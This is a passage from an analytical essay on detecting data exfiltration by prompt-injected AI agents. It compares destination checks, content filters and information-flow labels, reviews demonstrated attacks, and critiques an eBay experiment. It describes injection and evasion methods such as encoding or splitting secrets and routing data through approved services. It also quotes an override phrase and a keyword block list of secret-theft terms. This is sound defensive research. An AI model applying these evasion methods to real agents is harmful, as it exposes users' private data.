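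Both techniques have legitimate uses. People forward mail to an assistant while they are on holiday, and Microsoft lets administrators send silent copies of suspected impersonation emails to other addresses, presumably for a security team to examine.

### Rare and recently registered domains

For websites, a company can get much of the relevant history from logs it may already keep. A proxy or DNS server records which computer requested which domain and when. A security team can use these records to find when anyone in the company first contacted a domain and how many computers have contacted it since. The domain's public registration record usually shows when it was registered.

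A simple rarity score is log₂(*N* ÷ *n*), where *N* is the number of computers in the company and *n* is the number that contacted the domain during, say, the past month. In a company with 5,000 computers, a domain that half of them contacted scores 1, and a domain that only one contacted scores about 12.3. The company can then add points if the domain is only a few days old. Zilberman and colleagues use a similar formula to give unusual words more weight when they compare emails.

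Domain age and rarity are useful together because legitimate sites that look suspicious on one measure often look normal on the other. Sites for small businesses, local clubs and specialist manuals may be rare on a company's network but have had the same domain for years. A large company's product site may be new but attract many visitors on its first day. A domain that an attacker registers for one theft is both new and rare.

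An attacker can improve the age score by buying an older domain, as in Ana's case. Using a shared service improves both scores. `docs.google.com` is old and nearly everyone contacts it, so the form that received Superhuman users' emails would have scored as ordinary. To flag that form, the team would need to decrypt traffic with a proxy and count visits to the form itself.

Agents also change what counts as normal. A research agent may open dozens of obscure pages in an afternoon, most of which nobody else in the company has visited. If the company logs those visits together with its staff's, visits to rare domains become common. Conversely, an injection on a popular page could send a hundred agents to `collector.example` in one morning, which would make the domain look well used. Keeping separate records for people and agents would reduce both problems.

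### Sites that fit the task

Google's Chrome browser checks whether a site belongs to an agent's current task. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes the design, called Agent Origin Sets, which Google announced on 8 December 2025 for an agent that can click and type on web pages. An origin is the combination of scheme, host and port number that browsers use to separate websites. Browsers normally stop a page from one origin from reading a page from another, but an agent that works across many sites could undo that protection by carrying data between them.

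In the full design, Chrome keeps two sets of origins for each session. The agent can only read pages from read-only origins, but it can also click and type on read-writable ones. When Ana asks for a comparison of two hotels, the model that plans the work proposes sites to use. A separate gating function decides which are relevant and sorts those into the two sets. The gate must also approve any new site before the planner can open it or a page can send the agent there.

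The gate receives no untrusted page content, so hidden text on a hotel page can't influence it directly, though the text may still lead the planner to propose `collector.example`. This also leaves the gate with less information. It might reject `collector.example` because the name has nothing to do with hotels, but accept the same attacker's `hotel-points.example` because it can't read the page to see what the site does. Parker acknowledges this trade-off for a related Chrome component, which reviews the agent's actions with less context but also has a simpler job.

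The readable and writable sets also limit what a successful attack can reach. Chrome doesn't show the model advertisements or other embedded frames from origins outside the readable set. The model can pass on what it reads only to writable origins. Chrome's exact-URL check separately guards against data hidden in URLs that the model writes.

The first version tracked only the read-writable set, so it limited where the agent could act but not what it could read. Parker explains that it is hard to find the right balance before seeing how the restrictions affect people's tasks, and that Google planned to adjust the gate to reduce unnecessary friction.

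*Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (Roesner and Kohlbrenner, 2026) describes an attack that shows why it matters what an agent can read. The user visits the attacker's page, which contains a frame from another site, such as a bank. When the user asks for a summary, hidden instructions lead the agent to include the bank's content and type the summary into a form on the page. The form then submits itself, sending the data to a site the user has already opened and asked about. A warning about new destinations would not appear, and a gate that checked relevance might well classify the page as part of the task. Hiding the bank's frame from the model, as Chrome's full design would, prevents the agent from reading the data the attacker wants.

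Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested seven browsers with AI assistants in January and February 2026. They demonstrated the theft on OpenAI's Atlas in its agent mode. Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Perplexity's Comet met the preconditions for it, but they did not carry out the full attack on those three. The attack also requires a successful injection and a sensitive site that allows other pages to embed it, although an advertisement could attack the page around it in the same way.

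### A declared trust boundary

Claude Code's auto mode starts from what the user has declared trusted. A separate model, called a classifier, approves or blocks the coding agent's riskier actions so that the user doesn't have to approve each one. According to Anthropic, sessions in the terminal and the VS Code editor now start in auto mode by default.

According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the classifier by default trusts only the git repository the user is working in, meaning that project's code and its history of changes. Users can also mark their company's GitHub organisation, storage buckets, domains and internal services as trusted. The classifier treats everything else as external and a possible place for data to leak. One of its more than twenty default rules prohibits sending data to a service the user never specified.

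The boundary can be more precise than a list of domains. A company can declare its own GitHub organisation trusted without trusting every account on `github.com`. In one example from Anthropic's internal records, an agent prepared to post a script as a GitHub Gist, a page for sharing snippets of code, to share it for debugging. Auto mode would block this because the user might consider the script confidential, even though programmers use GitHub every day.

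The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's actions, but not the agent's explanations or the pages and files the agent has read. If a file tells the agent to send passwords to some address "for validation", the classifier receives only the agent's attempt to send passwords to an outside address the user didn't mention, without the stated reason. The drawback is that the classifier can't always tell where a name came from. For instance, it can't distinguish an address the agent looked up in the company directory from one the agent made up.

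When an action is blocked, the session continues, and the agent receives the reason and an instruction to find a safer method without trying to get around the block. After three consecutive blocks, or 20 in total, Claude Code stops the agent and asks the user. If the agent is running without an interface for asking the user, the program ends.

The classifier is a model, so the boundary depends on its judgement and is less firm than a sandbox without network access. In Anthropic's tests, the classifier let through 5.7% of artificial attempts to steal data. Unlike methods based on history, a declared boundary works on the first day. But someone has to declare it accurately, and a company that lists too much faces the same problems as with a broad domain allowlist.

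### When history is empty, planted or misleading

A new employee or an agent with a fresh mailbox has no past correspondence, so every address is new. Zilberman and colleagues found that short histories also caused errors with known contacts, because a few brief emails are not enough to show what two people normally discuss. Using the whole organisation's past correspondence helps a new employee at a large company, but not someone who works alone. In *How to hide yellow external warning label in Gmail iPhone app?*, a question on a Google community forum, the owner of a one-person organisation complains that all emails count as "external" and calls the label useless.

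Sharing history across an organisation can also reveal who writes to whom. Microsoft warns of this risk with its first contact tip. When a message goes to several people, the tip can show that some of them don't often hear from the sender, so each recipient learns something about the others. A company-wide check on an agent's recipients could expose similar information if its decisions came with detailed explanations.

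An attacker can create a contact history by emailing the user first. Android Central's *Gmail releases visual updates to its compose window after a long delay* says that Gmail counts an outside contact as known if the user has sent them an email or received one from them. If so, an email carrying an injection would also make its sender a known contact. If an agent then replied with stolen data, Gmail would show the yellow highlight but no banner. Google's announcement says only "interacted with", which doesn't settle whether receiving an email is enough.

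Some of Microsoft's impersonation protections also stop applying once two people have communicated by email, at least when the organisation turns on the setting that learns from its users' mail.

Counting only messages that the user has sent prevents an attacker from becoming a known contact just by writing first. This isn't enough if the agent answers routine mail by itself, because the attacker can ask a harmless question on Monday, get a reply, and send the injection on Thursday. The check should therefore ignore replies that no person wrote or approved. It could also require several exchanges over a few weeks, but a patient attacker can manage that, and honest new contacts would trigger warnings for longer. Gmail's older reply warning is stricter in that it looks for regular contact. But dismissing it once silences it permanently for that address, so a user who dismisses it to send one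 harmless reply gets no warning on later replies.

Messages to familiar recipients can also leak data. Carvalho and Cohen recall that in 2001 the office of California's governor accidentally emailed confidential figures on the state's electricity purchases to reporters on its own press list. The office had presumably written to those reporters many times. The recipient in the Copilot Cowork attack was familiar too, because it was the user.

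In one incident in Anthropic's records, with no attacker involved, an agent trying to be helpful uploaded an engineer's GitHub access token to one of the company's own computing clusters. The upload was a mistake because the file contained a credential. A warning based on the company's past traffic would probably have missed it, since its engineers normally sent files to that cluster.

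## Whether stolen data goes to new destinations

The value of a warning about new destinations depends on how often thieves use them. The invented example above assumed that 90% of thefts send data somewhere new. If only 10% did, and 5% of honest actions still did, a new destination would only double the odds of theft.

Published research doesn't give the percentage of real thefts that send data to new destinations. The closest substitute is the set of attacks researchers have demonstrated, twelve of which appear below. Willison's log of exfiltration attacks records where the data went in most of them.

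In the table, a domain is new if the product had not approved it and the victim was not already using it through the product. A URL is new if the full address did not exist before the attack. A recipient or account is new if the data went to a server, form or account belonging to someone the victim had never dealt with.

| Attack | Exit channel | Receiving host | New domain? | New exact URL? | New recipient or account? |
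|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Image | A Microsoft Teams server | No | Yes | Yes |
| SearchLeak | Image | `bing.com` | No | Yes | Yes |
| ForcedLeak | Image | `my-salesforce-cms.com` | No | Yes | Yes |
| Superhuman | Image | `docs.google.com` | No | Yes | Yes |
| Antigravity | Page opened in the agent's browser | `webhook.site` | No | Yes | Yes |
| Claude Cowork | File upload | `api.anthropic.com` | No | No | Yes |
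| GitHub project names | Change proposed to a public project | `github.com` | No | No | No |
| Copilot Cowork | Image in a message to the user | The attacker's server | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Claude and the coffee shop | Page fetch | The attacker's website | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| GitLab Duo | Image | `legitsecurity.com` | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Cursor and the Jira ticket | Page fetch | A site on `azurewebsites.net` | Yes | Yes | Yes |
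| Operator | Text typed into a page | Rehberger's own website | Yes | No | Yes |
| **Flagged** | | | **5 of 12** | **9 of 12** | **11 of 12** |

People can therefore use the same twelve attacks to argue that novelty is a weak signal, citing 42%, or a strong one, citing 92%.

The count also depends on how a check defines a familiar domain or URL. Salesforce's policy still approved the domain in ForcedLeak, but the registration had lapsed, so a company's traffic log would probably have shown no recent visits. Few Antigravity users outside software testing will have visited `webhook.site` either. A check based on each user's own history might therefore flag seven domains. In the Cursor attack, the token went to a site on `azurewebsites.net`, where Microsoft hosts its customers' websites. A check that used only the last two parts of the name would match a familiar Microsoft domain and miss the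 attack. The exact-URL count would fall to eight under the rule Anthropic used at the time, which accepted the coffee shop's links.

The eleven in the last column make recipient checks look better than they are, because an attacker is, almost by definition, a stranger to the victim. It is harder for software to identify that stranger. In the Claude Cowork attack, for example, the attacker's only trace was an access key.

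A warning about first-time email recipients, like Gmail's, would have flagged none of the twelve, because none involved a message to a stranger. SmarterArticles' *Your AI Agent Will Be Compromised* (2026) describes an attack that did, which the security company Invariant Labs demonstrated in April 2025. A malicious tool made an agent send its user's WhatsApp history to the attacker's phone number, a new recipient on a familiar service.

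No column flags the GitHub attack, because the agent published the project names in its user's own public project, a familiar destination that anyone could read.

### Why the counts are not a rate

Researchers look for a way past whatever check a product has. In six of the twelve attacks (the first six in the table), the product restricted which domains the relevant channel could contact. All six used an approved domain, because a request to an unapproved one, such as `collector.example`, would have failed and left the researcher with no working attack to publish.

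No domain list restricted the other six attacks, and five of them used a new domain. In the sixth, the GitHub attack, the agent's tool could write only to GitHub.

| Did the product restrict domains? | Attacks | Used a new domain |
|---|---|---|
| Yes | 6 | 0 |
| No | 6 | 5 |

The overall figure of five in twelve therefore depends mostly on how many protected products are in the sample. When researchers have a free choice, they usually set up their own server, which is the easiest way to collect data, though the Codex attack used a Google form instead. If more products began to block new domains, attackers would probably adapt in the same way, so a measurement taken before that change would overstate how useful the signal is afterwards.

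The exact-URL column has the same weakness, though less visibly. Of the twelve products, only Claude's chat app applied an exact-URL rule to the request in question. After OpenAI restricted the URLs ChatGPT could open, Radware switched to a set of ready-made URLs. If most products checked exact URLs, a later set of twelve attacks would probably include many more like Radware's, and the check would flag fewer than nine of the twelve.

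The count also depends on which attacks are included. PromptArmor found four of the twelve, so one company's methods have a large influence on the result. An attack that loads an image from the researcher's own server is also less interesting to write about than one that abuses a trusted service. Willison calls one report of an image-loading attack, on Antigravity, "an old classic". Adding two demonstrations by the browser company Brave, against the AI browsers Comet and Fellou, would raise the domain count to seven of fourteen, because both sent data to the same unfamiliar site, `uaf.cafe`.

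Nearly all disclosed cases are also demonstrations, and a researcher's reasons for choosing a destination differ from a thief's. Rehberger can send Operator to a website he openly runs. A thief has to avoid being traced and keep the collection point working until the data arrives. A free online form is quick to create and abandon, but its provider can close it and may keep records of who set it up. A private server gives the thief more control but requires a domain that security companies can block. Demonstrations don't show which a thief would prefer.

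Laboratory tests also can't show whether stolen data goes to new destinations if the testers choose the destination. Willison describes a Google DeepMind evaluation that uses a planted email to try to make an agent send private details, such as a passport number, to an attacker-controlled address. Every successful theft in that test goes to a new recipient because the testers set it up that way.

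### Injections on the open web

A few studies have looked for injections that people have actually planted. The largest, *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang et al., 2026), searched about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. That half contained 1.2 billion URLs on 24.8 million hosts. The study also used results from Censys and Shodan, two services that scan the internet for connected machines.

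The researchers searched for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injections, such as variations on "ignore your instructions", and found 31,206 matches. Many came from tutorials or articles about prompt injection. Two reviewers, using software that grouped similar matches, confirmed 15,387 as genuine instructions to a machine, on 11,722 pages across 2,042 hosts. In the Common Crawl part of the sample, about eight pages in a million contained a genuine instruction.

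Only 13 of the 15,387 injections aimed at data theft, or about 0.08%. The share by host is higher, at 10 of 2,042, or about 0.5%. Hosts are arguably the better unit because a site's operator can copy one instruction onto thousands of pages, and 54 templates account for 95% of the injections. More than half of the injections instead tried to disrupt the AI system, usually by making it produce nonsense, and many others told it not to reuse the page's content.

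Nine of the 13 asked for the system prompt, the instructions a developer gives a model, and four asked for secrets such as access keys. The paper prints four examples of attempted theft. Two give an email address as the destination, and one tells the model to post secret keys on a public forum or social media. The fourth asks the model to reveal its system prompt but gives no destination, so it could work only if the attacker can read the model's answer, as in a customer-support chat.

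For nearly any user, an email address on a stranger's web page would be a first-time recipient. A warning like Gmail's would therefore fit two of the three printed examples that name a destination, though it would have flagged none of the twelve demonstrations. Three examples are too few to give a percentage, and one of them also asks for a limerick about cheese, so its author may not have expected to steal anything. But they suggest that crude attempts are easier to catch by destination than the attacks researchers publish.

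Injections that don't try to steal data can also cause requests to unfamiliar sites. Khodayari and colleagues found 598 traps for AI bots on 18 hosts, 46 times the number of theft attempts. The traps tell an agent to contact an outside address or do something else that reveals it is a bot. In one example, the agent has to request a page and include its model name and the answer to a sum in the URL. Both a new-domain check and an exact-URL check would flag this request. The flag would be correct in that a web page had taken control of the agent, but the site's owner would learn only that a bot had visited.

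The researchers also tested whether models obey such text by giving 13 models 100 of the injections, each in four page formats, and asking for a summary of the page. The models followed the injection in 81 of 5,200 runs, or 1.6%. Small models reading plain text did so 8% of the time. The models had no tools for sending data, so the test didn't measure where they would send it, but it shows that a typical injection on the web is weak.

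Three company reports give a similar picture:

- Google scanned several editions of Common Crawl, used its Gemini model to classify suspicious text, and had people review the results. It found a small number of theft attempts and no significant use of the methods that researchers published in 2025. Its example came from a website author running an experiment. Injections it classed as malicious, which include attempts to delete files as well as to steal data, rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026.
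- Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, described twelve live cases. One sought a company's contact details, while four tried to make an agent pay for something or subscribe to it.
- Sewani, in *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, describes ten cases found by the security company Forcepoint. One asked for an API key to be sent to "me", with no address given in the description. It also told the model not to reveal "the flag", the usual name for the hidden answer in a hacking puzzle. Sewani treats it as an attack, but it may have been part of a game.

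Payment attacks offer some evidence about familiar hosts. Unit 42 and Sewani both found a page that told agents to send $5,000 to a PayPal account, and both found pages that sent agents to payment links on Stripe, which is also well known. A domain check would treat these destinations as trusted, and only a check on the account could show that the recipient was unfamiliar. Sewani infers that the attacker chose PayPal because a model may judge whether a URL looks trustworthy. A simpler explanation is that anyone who wants to be paid online needs a payment service. Data thieves don't need one, so these cases are little evidence of which destinations they would choose. The same applies to the sites that tried to make agents pay in cryptocurrency, described in Mascellino's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (2026).

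The web studies can't correct the bias in the twelve demonstrations, because they mostly sample different places. In seven of the twelve, the instructions arrived through an email, form, file or link sent to the victim, where a web crawler would not find them. A crawler would also miss the coffee-shop attack, because that site showed its instructions only to Claude. Searches for known phrases miss carefully worded instructions, such as the EchoLeak email, which read like ordinary business correspondence. Attackers skilled enough to use a familiar service can probably stay out of these samples too.

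### Confirmed thefts

The clearest real case is the malicious email tool `postmark-mcp`, which sent blind copies of emails to a new recipient at a new domain. This fits the pattern of attackers using their own domain when nothing stops them. But the attack didn't use injection, and the publisher had no evident need to disguise the destination because the agent never handled the copies.

News reports of data theft "by AI agents" often describe agents working for the thief rather than hijacked ones. *AI Agents Used to Steal 600K+ Credit-Card Records* (Ofonagoro, 2026) reports that one operator used agents to automate more than 100 attacks, broke into 27 organisations and stole over 600,000 card records. *AI Agent Carries Out Multi-Stage Data Theft Attack* (Muncaster, 2026) says that Spain's data protection agency has reported the country's first breach of this kind. The agent in that case also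 appears to have worked for the thief. A check on the victim's own agent would not detect such a theft, so neither case helps to estimate how often hijacked agents send data to new destinations.

Thefts through hijacked agents may become more common. In *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, Underhill (2026) reported in August that criminals were developing tools for such thefts. According to figures cited by SmarterArticles, the security company Check Point's detections of indirect injection rose about fivefold between March and May 2026, to nearly 1% of the prompts it observed. However, these figures cover only attempts and don't include where any data was supposed to go.

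### Data that would settle the question

A useful dataset would start from thefts discovered without a destination check, for example because someone used a stolen password. Otherwise, the data would leave out thefts through familiar services, which the check misses. For each theft, investigators would need to record the domain, the full URL and the receiving account, and whether each was new to the user and to the organisation. They would also need to record which checks the product applied, because the pattern differs so much between products with and without domain lists.

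A sample of 100 independent thefts would be enough to estimate the share that went somewhere new, with a margin of error of at most about ten percentage points. The thefts need to be independent because one criminal group might steal from a thousand users through the same form, and those thefts would count as little more than one observation of how attackers choose a destination.

Companies that run agents probably have some of this information in their logs and incident reports. They could publish the counts without naming customers or revealing the addresses. Blocked attempts would be worth including because published research mostly leaves them out, but companies would have to confirm which were really attacks.

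Researchers could also collect the data themselves by planting decoys. *Researchers fed AI 2 million secrets. Strangers used them* (BagheeraAltered, 2026) summarises an experiment in which the security company Dragos sent about two million prompts to AI services between July and November 2026. Each prompt contained unique web addresses and decoy credentials. Outsiders later opened the addresses and used credentials for Amazon's cloud service. Dragos was looking for leaks by the AI services and their suppliers, not by hijacked agents, but researchers could put similar decoys in mailboxes and folders that an agent can read.

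If someone then used a planted credential, the researchers would know about the theft wherever the data went, and could search the agent's logs for the request that carried it. This would miss thieves who never use what they steal and those who recognise a decoy. The researchers could also run half of the decoy agents with a domain list and half without, which would show how often real attackers switch to a familiar service when a new domain fails.

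## Whether inspecting the content adds to checking the destination

If thieves can collect data through familiar services, inspecting the data being sent may work better than checking its destination. *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries* (2026) describes a case from March 2023, when Samsung employees pasted semiconductor source code into ChatGPT. Nobody had hijacked anything and the site was well known, so the requests were a problem only because of their content.

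An agent can make the same kind of mistake. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes attacks that need no hidden instructions, because an outsider asks the agent for help. In one scenario, an agent knows a man's mental-health diagnosis. His ex-wife creates a shared page in Notion, a workspace app, and invites the agent to fill in a section with professional notes, and the agent writes about his health. If she is a regular contact and Notion is an approved service, a warning about new destinations would not appear. Three attacks of this type extracted between 44% and 76% of the private items from agents given strict written instructions for checking identity and consent.

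### Keywords and entropy

The simplest content check searches outgoing requests for suspicious words. The keyword filter in *Silent Egress* blocks any URL that contains "password", "secret", "token", "auth" or a few similar strings. It would miss Ana's card number in `ref=48213`, and it would block `library.example/authors/austen`, because "authors" contains "auth".

A company can instead search for the secrets themselves, if it has a list of them. *The Framing Gap* tested how well this works when the injected instructions also tell the model to disguise the secret. GPT-4o could produce five of the six encodings requested, and with no guard it leaked the secret in 56.7% of runs. A guard that searched for the exact text reduced this only to 50.0%, because it caught only the undisguised secret. An improved guard that could undo reversed text, added separators, base64 and hexadecimal stopped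 all of those. But it missed every leak in ROT13, a simple cipher that moves each letter 13 places along the alphabet, which the researchers had deliberately left out. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) points out that these scanners also pass text that hides a key in its spacing.

An entropy test looks for values that seem random, as passwords and access keys often do, without needing to know the secret. It measures how varied the characters are:

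`H = −Σ p × log₂ p`

Here *p* is one character's share of the value, and the sum runs over each different character. In 48213 each of the five digits has a share of 1/5, so *H* is log₂ 5, or about 2.32 bits per character.

The filter in *Silent Egress* blocks a URL parameter if it has more than ten characters and an entropy above 4.0. The study's own sample key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, would pass. It has 20 characters. The letter E and the underscore appear three times each, and 14 other characters appear once:

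`H = 14 × (1/20) × log₂ 20 + 2 × (3/20) × log₂ (20/3) ≈ 3.03 + 0.82 = 3.85`

Encoding this key in base64 raises its entropy to 4.09, which the entropy filter would block. The two filters therefore partly compensate for each other's gaps, since a disguise that removes the keywords can make the value look more random. But reversing the key removes the keywords and leaves the entropy at 3.85, so a reversed key passes both filters.

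Secrets of 16 characters or fewer, including most passwords, always pass this entropy test. A value with *m* characters has an entropy of at most log₂ *m*, so theirs cannot exceed 4.0. A lower threshold would catch more of them but would also flag more legitimate addresses, such as links to shared documents, which often contain long random identifiers. A model could instead judge the meaning of the outgoing text. According to *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries*, this produces more false alarms than fixed rules and often requires the software to read people's files.

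### Rules about who may read what

Two systems from 2025, Microsoft's FIDES and Google DeepMind's CaMeL, record where each piece of data came from and who may read it, and check that record before any data leaves. This approach, called information-flow control, means they don't have to recognise secrets.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) explains FIDES with the example of a user who asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. In one of the emails, an attacker tells the agent to forward the top message in the mailbox to an outside address.

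FIDES gives each email two labels, one for whether the text is trusted and one for who may read it, normally the sender and the recipients. When the agent combines data, only people who could read all of it may read the result. If Ana, Bob and the manager received one email but only Ana and Bob received another, only Ana and Bob may read a summary of both.

The model that plans the work never has to read the emails. FIDES stores their text in variables, and the planner uses only the variables' names. A second model, which has no tools, writes the summary. FIDES then allows the planner to send an email if either of two conditions holds:

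- Everyone who will receive the message may read its content, and the message contains no untrusted link.
- No untrusted text had reached the planner when it decided to send the message.

The summary meets the second condition, so the manager gets it despite not having received one of the emails. If the planner opened the attacker's email and tried to obey it, the message would meet neither condition and FIDES would block it. Encoding the stolen text first would make no difference, because the labels stay with the data.

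Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that CaMeL's planner turns the user's request into a short program before anything is fetched. CaMeL's own interpreter then runs the program and tracks which values each new value depends on. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) describes the label this tracking gives each value as a pair, made up of the sources that influenced the value and the components that may read it.

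In the example, the manager's address comes from the user, so CaMeL can send the summary. If the user had instead asked the agent to send it to whoever requested it, the agent would have to take the address from an email, where an attacker could have planted it. CaMeL would then send the message without asking only if the user's policy already trusted that address. This is more selective than the warning about first-time recipients. Ana could type a new customer's address without being asked to confirm it, but she would be asked if the same address came from an untrusted email.

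Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in four simulated settings. Without the rules, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent running GPT-4o, and with them none did. But the protection makes agents somewhat less able to complete honest tasks. The table shows the share of these tasks that agents completed with OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, when nobody was attacking.

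| Setting | Ordinary agent, no rules | Ordinary agent with rules | FIDES with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 70.0% | 48.0% | 64.5% |
| Travel | 82.0% | 75.0% | 68.0% |
| Banking | 96.2% | 37.5% | 56.2% |
| Slack | 87.6% | 17.1% | 54.3% |

FIDES completed about 62% of tasks and the unprotected agent about 81%, averaged across settings and weighted by the number of tasks in each. Some of the loss is unavoidable because many of the banking tasks require the agent to follow instructions in a file, for example to schedule a payment, and FIDES can't distinguish this from an injection.

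*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL on 112 tasks in which several agents work together. CaMeL lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The tests used no rules about recipients, so these drops reflect only the effect of planning without seeing the data. Recipient rules would presumably block some further tasks. Someone also has to write those rules and keep them up to date, which worries Willison, who finds such policies hard to get right himself.

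The labels also record only where data could have gone. As *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) explains, FIDES treats a path from a source to a destination as strong evidence that data travelled along it, and doesn't reconstruct what happened in the model's reasoning. It can therefore block a message that contains nothing private if the planner read something private earlier.

### The eBay experiment

*Silent Egress*, which researchers at eBay published in February 2026, compared content checks and destination checks against the same attack. The researchers used a local test system with synthetic secrets and an agent running qwen2.5:7b, a small open model. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a web page, which the agent's software fetched automatically. The page contained instructions to send the secret in a web request, supposedly to verify the agent's connection. The researchers' server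 recorded the requests it received.

They varied where the instructions appeared (in the page's title, description, body or link text), whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether it had to send the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 resulting configurations 30 times.

The agent sent a request to the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1%. In 95% of these successful attacks, the answer looked harmless. Redirects made almost no difference to the success rate, which was 89% with them and 88% without.

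The researchers then tested defences on one configuration, with the instructions in the page body, no redirect and the secret sent whole. Each row below covers 30 runs.

| Defence | Agent tried to send | Request got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Hardened system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Delimiters around web content | 100% | 100% |
| Hardened prompt and delimiters | 56.7% | 56.7% |
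| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Entropy filter | 0% | 0% |
| All of these together | 0% | 0% |

The hardened prompt, an instruction for the model to treat web content as data and follow only the user, failed in 20 of 30 runs. Delimiters marking the fetched text as untrusted had no effect by themselves. Adding them to the hardened prompt reduced the failures to 17, a difference that could easily be chance.

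### Why the defence comparison proves less than it seems to

The allowlist's perfect score follows from the design of the test. The list had four domains, and the researchers chose `evil-collector.net` as the attacker's address because it was clearly not one of them. *The Framing Gap* reports the same 0% for its own list and states that this result holds by construction. If the attacker had used an account on an approved host, as in the attacks on Superhuman and Claude, the list would have let the data through. The eBay researchers acknowledge that attackers could use compromised sites or redirects on trusted ones, but they didn't test this.

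The experiment also can't show how many legitimate requests an allowlist would block, because the user only asked for a summary and no legitimate task required a new destination. The researchers report a false-positive rate of zero from 120 runs with harmless pages, in which the agent never contacted the attacker's server. Those runs confirm that the injected instructions caused the requests in the main experiment.

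The redirect detection blocked bare numerical addresses, eight domain endings such as `.xyz`, and any path containing a word such as "steal" or "collect". Despite its name, it did not trace redirects. The study's example attack uses the path `/collect`. If the defence test used the same path, the attacker could have got around the word check by renaming the path.

The results for the content filters are harder to explain. Both filters inspect a request after the agent has made it, so they shouldn't affect how often it tries to send the secret. Yet attempts fell from 100% to 23.3% with the keyword filter and to zero with the entropy filter. The researchers suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when someone is monitoring for them, but they don't explain how it would detect the monitoring. For the keyword filter, they suggest that the model sometimes disguised the secret. But a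 disguised secret would have passed the filter and reached the server, and none did. The software may have failed to count some blocked requests, or something may have revealed the filters to the model. Until someone finds the cause, the absence of leaks with either filter is not evidence that inspecting content works.

In *The Framing Gap*, the same qwen2.5:7b leaked the secret in only 10% of runs when the instructions were obvious, and in 62.5% when they presented the secret as a routine technical detail. The two test systems differ in several ways, including what they told the agent about protecting the secret, so the 88.1% reflects eBay's setup as much as the model. The eBay researchers call their success rates a lower bound because their injected instructions were simple, but they also say they deliberately made conditions favourable to the attacker, which would tend to raise those rates.

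### Splitting a secret across requests

An attacker can also avoid a content filter by having the agent send a secret in pieces, for example Ana's card number in five requests with one digit in each.

In eBay's experiment, splitting the secret made the attack less reliable. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 238 of 240 runs when it had to send the secret whole, but in 185 of 240 (77%) when it had to send four numbered pieces. A small model can lose track of a task with several steps, which may explain the drop.

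The study measures the attacker's benefit with Leak@*k*, the share of runs in which any sensitive data appears in the first *k* requests.

| How the agent sent the secret | Leak@1 | Leak@3 |
|---|---|---|
| Whole | 0.967 | 0.967 |
| In four pieces | 0.263 | 0.158 |

The researchers conclude that splitting reduces Leak@1 by 73%. But the second row shows Leak@3 lower than Leak@1, which is impossible under their definition, because a run with sensitive data in its first request also has sensitive data in its first three. Either a number is wrong or the software measured something else. It may have failed to classify the short pieces as sensitive, although any fragment counts under the definition.

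The study also defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which all the pieces arrive, but gives no value for it. An attacker would care about this figure most. Even the printed example is incomplete, since its four pieces contain only the first 16 of the sample key's 20 characters.

The researchers never ran the split attack against their filters, so their claim that it gets past simple content inspection rests on reasoning alone. The reasoning is sound, because pieces such as "SECR" and "ET_A" contain none of the keyword filter's strings, and the entropy filter ignores values this short. *The Framing Gap* doesn't test splitting either, because its agent takes only one step.

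A filter could combine everything an agent sends during a session, and the eBay researchers recommend comparing requests with one another and limiting how many an agent can make. These measures make it harder to split a secret across requests, but the filter still has to recognise the reassembled secret, which may be encoded or spread over several domains. A domain allowlist avoids this problem because it would refuse each of the five requests to `collector.example`. Information-flow labels also still work when a secret is split, because every piece inherits the label of the whole.

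### Tests on 2026 models

Current models resist simple injections much better than the model eBay used. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran 949 attacks against each of five models with no added defence. The attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time on GPT-4.1, but 1.5% on Claude Fable 5 and never on GPT-5.5. They warn that these attacks were fixed in advance, and that attackers who adapt their methods have had some success against every leading model in large tests. eBay's 88.1% is therefore a poor estimate for a current product, but how the checks behave once a model has been fooled is still relevant.

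In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) tested this in October on five recent models, including GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Opus 5.5. They built 28 linked websites, with 56 legitimate tasks and 56 attacks. As a worst case, they assumed that an attacker could choose a model's output whenever the model read untrusted text. They compared two main approaches. SOPGuard asks the user before an agent moves data from one site to another. SPIDES, their own system, labels individual parts of each page and applies rules similar to those of FIDES.

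Between 53% and 73% of the attacks succeeded against SOPGuard, depending on the model, and none succeeded against SPIDES. A check that only compares sites misses leaks within one site, such as when an agent posts private account details in a public comment. But the attacks also included unauthorised actions such as purchases, which no check on outgoing data is designed to stop, so the share of thefts SOPGuard would miss is lower than these percentages.

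SPIDES completed between 67% and 86% of the honest tasks and needed 1.84 user approvals per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard. It also relies on website owners to label their pages, which few would do without a strong reason. Because its labels list whole sites as permitted readers, it can't always distinguish two accounts on the same site. Tracking which content may leave doesn't help much if the recipient is identified only by site, as in a domain allowlist.

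### Which leaks need which check

| Leak | Searching the content | Allowing only listed domains | Tracking permitted readers |
|---|---|---|---|
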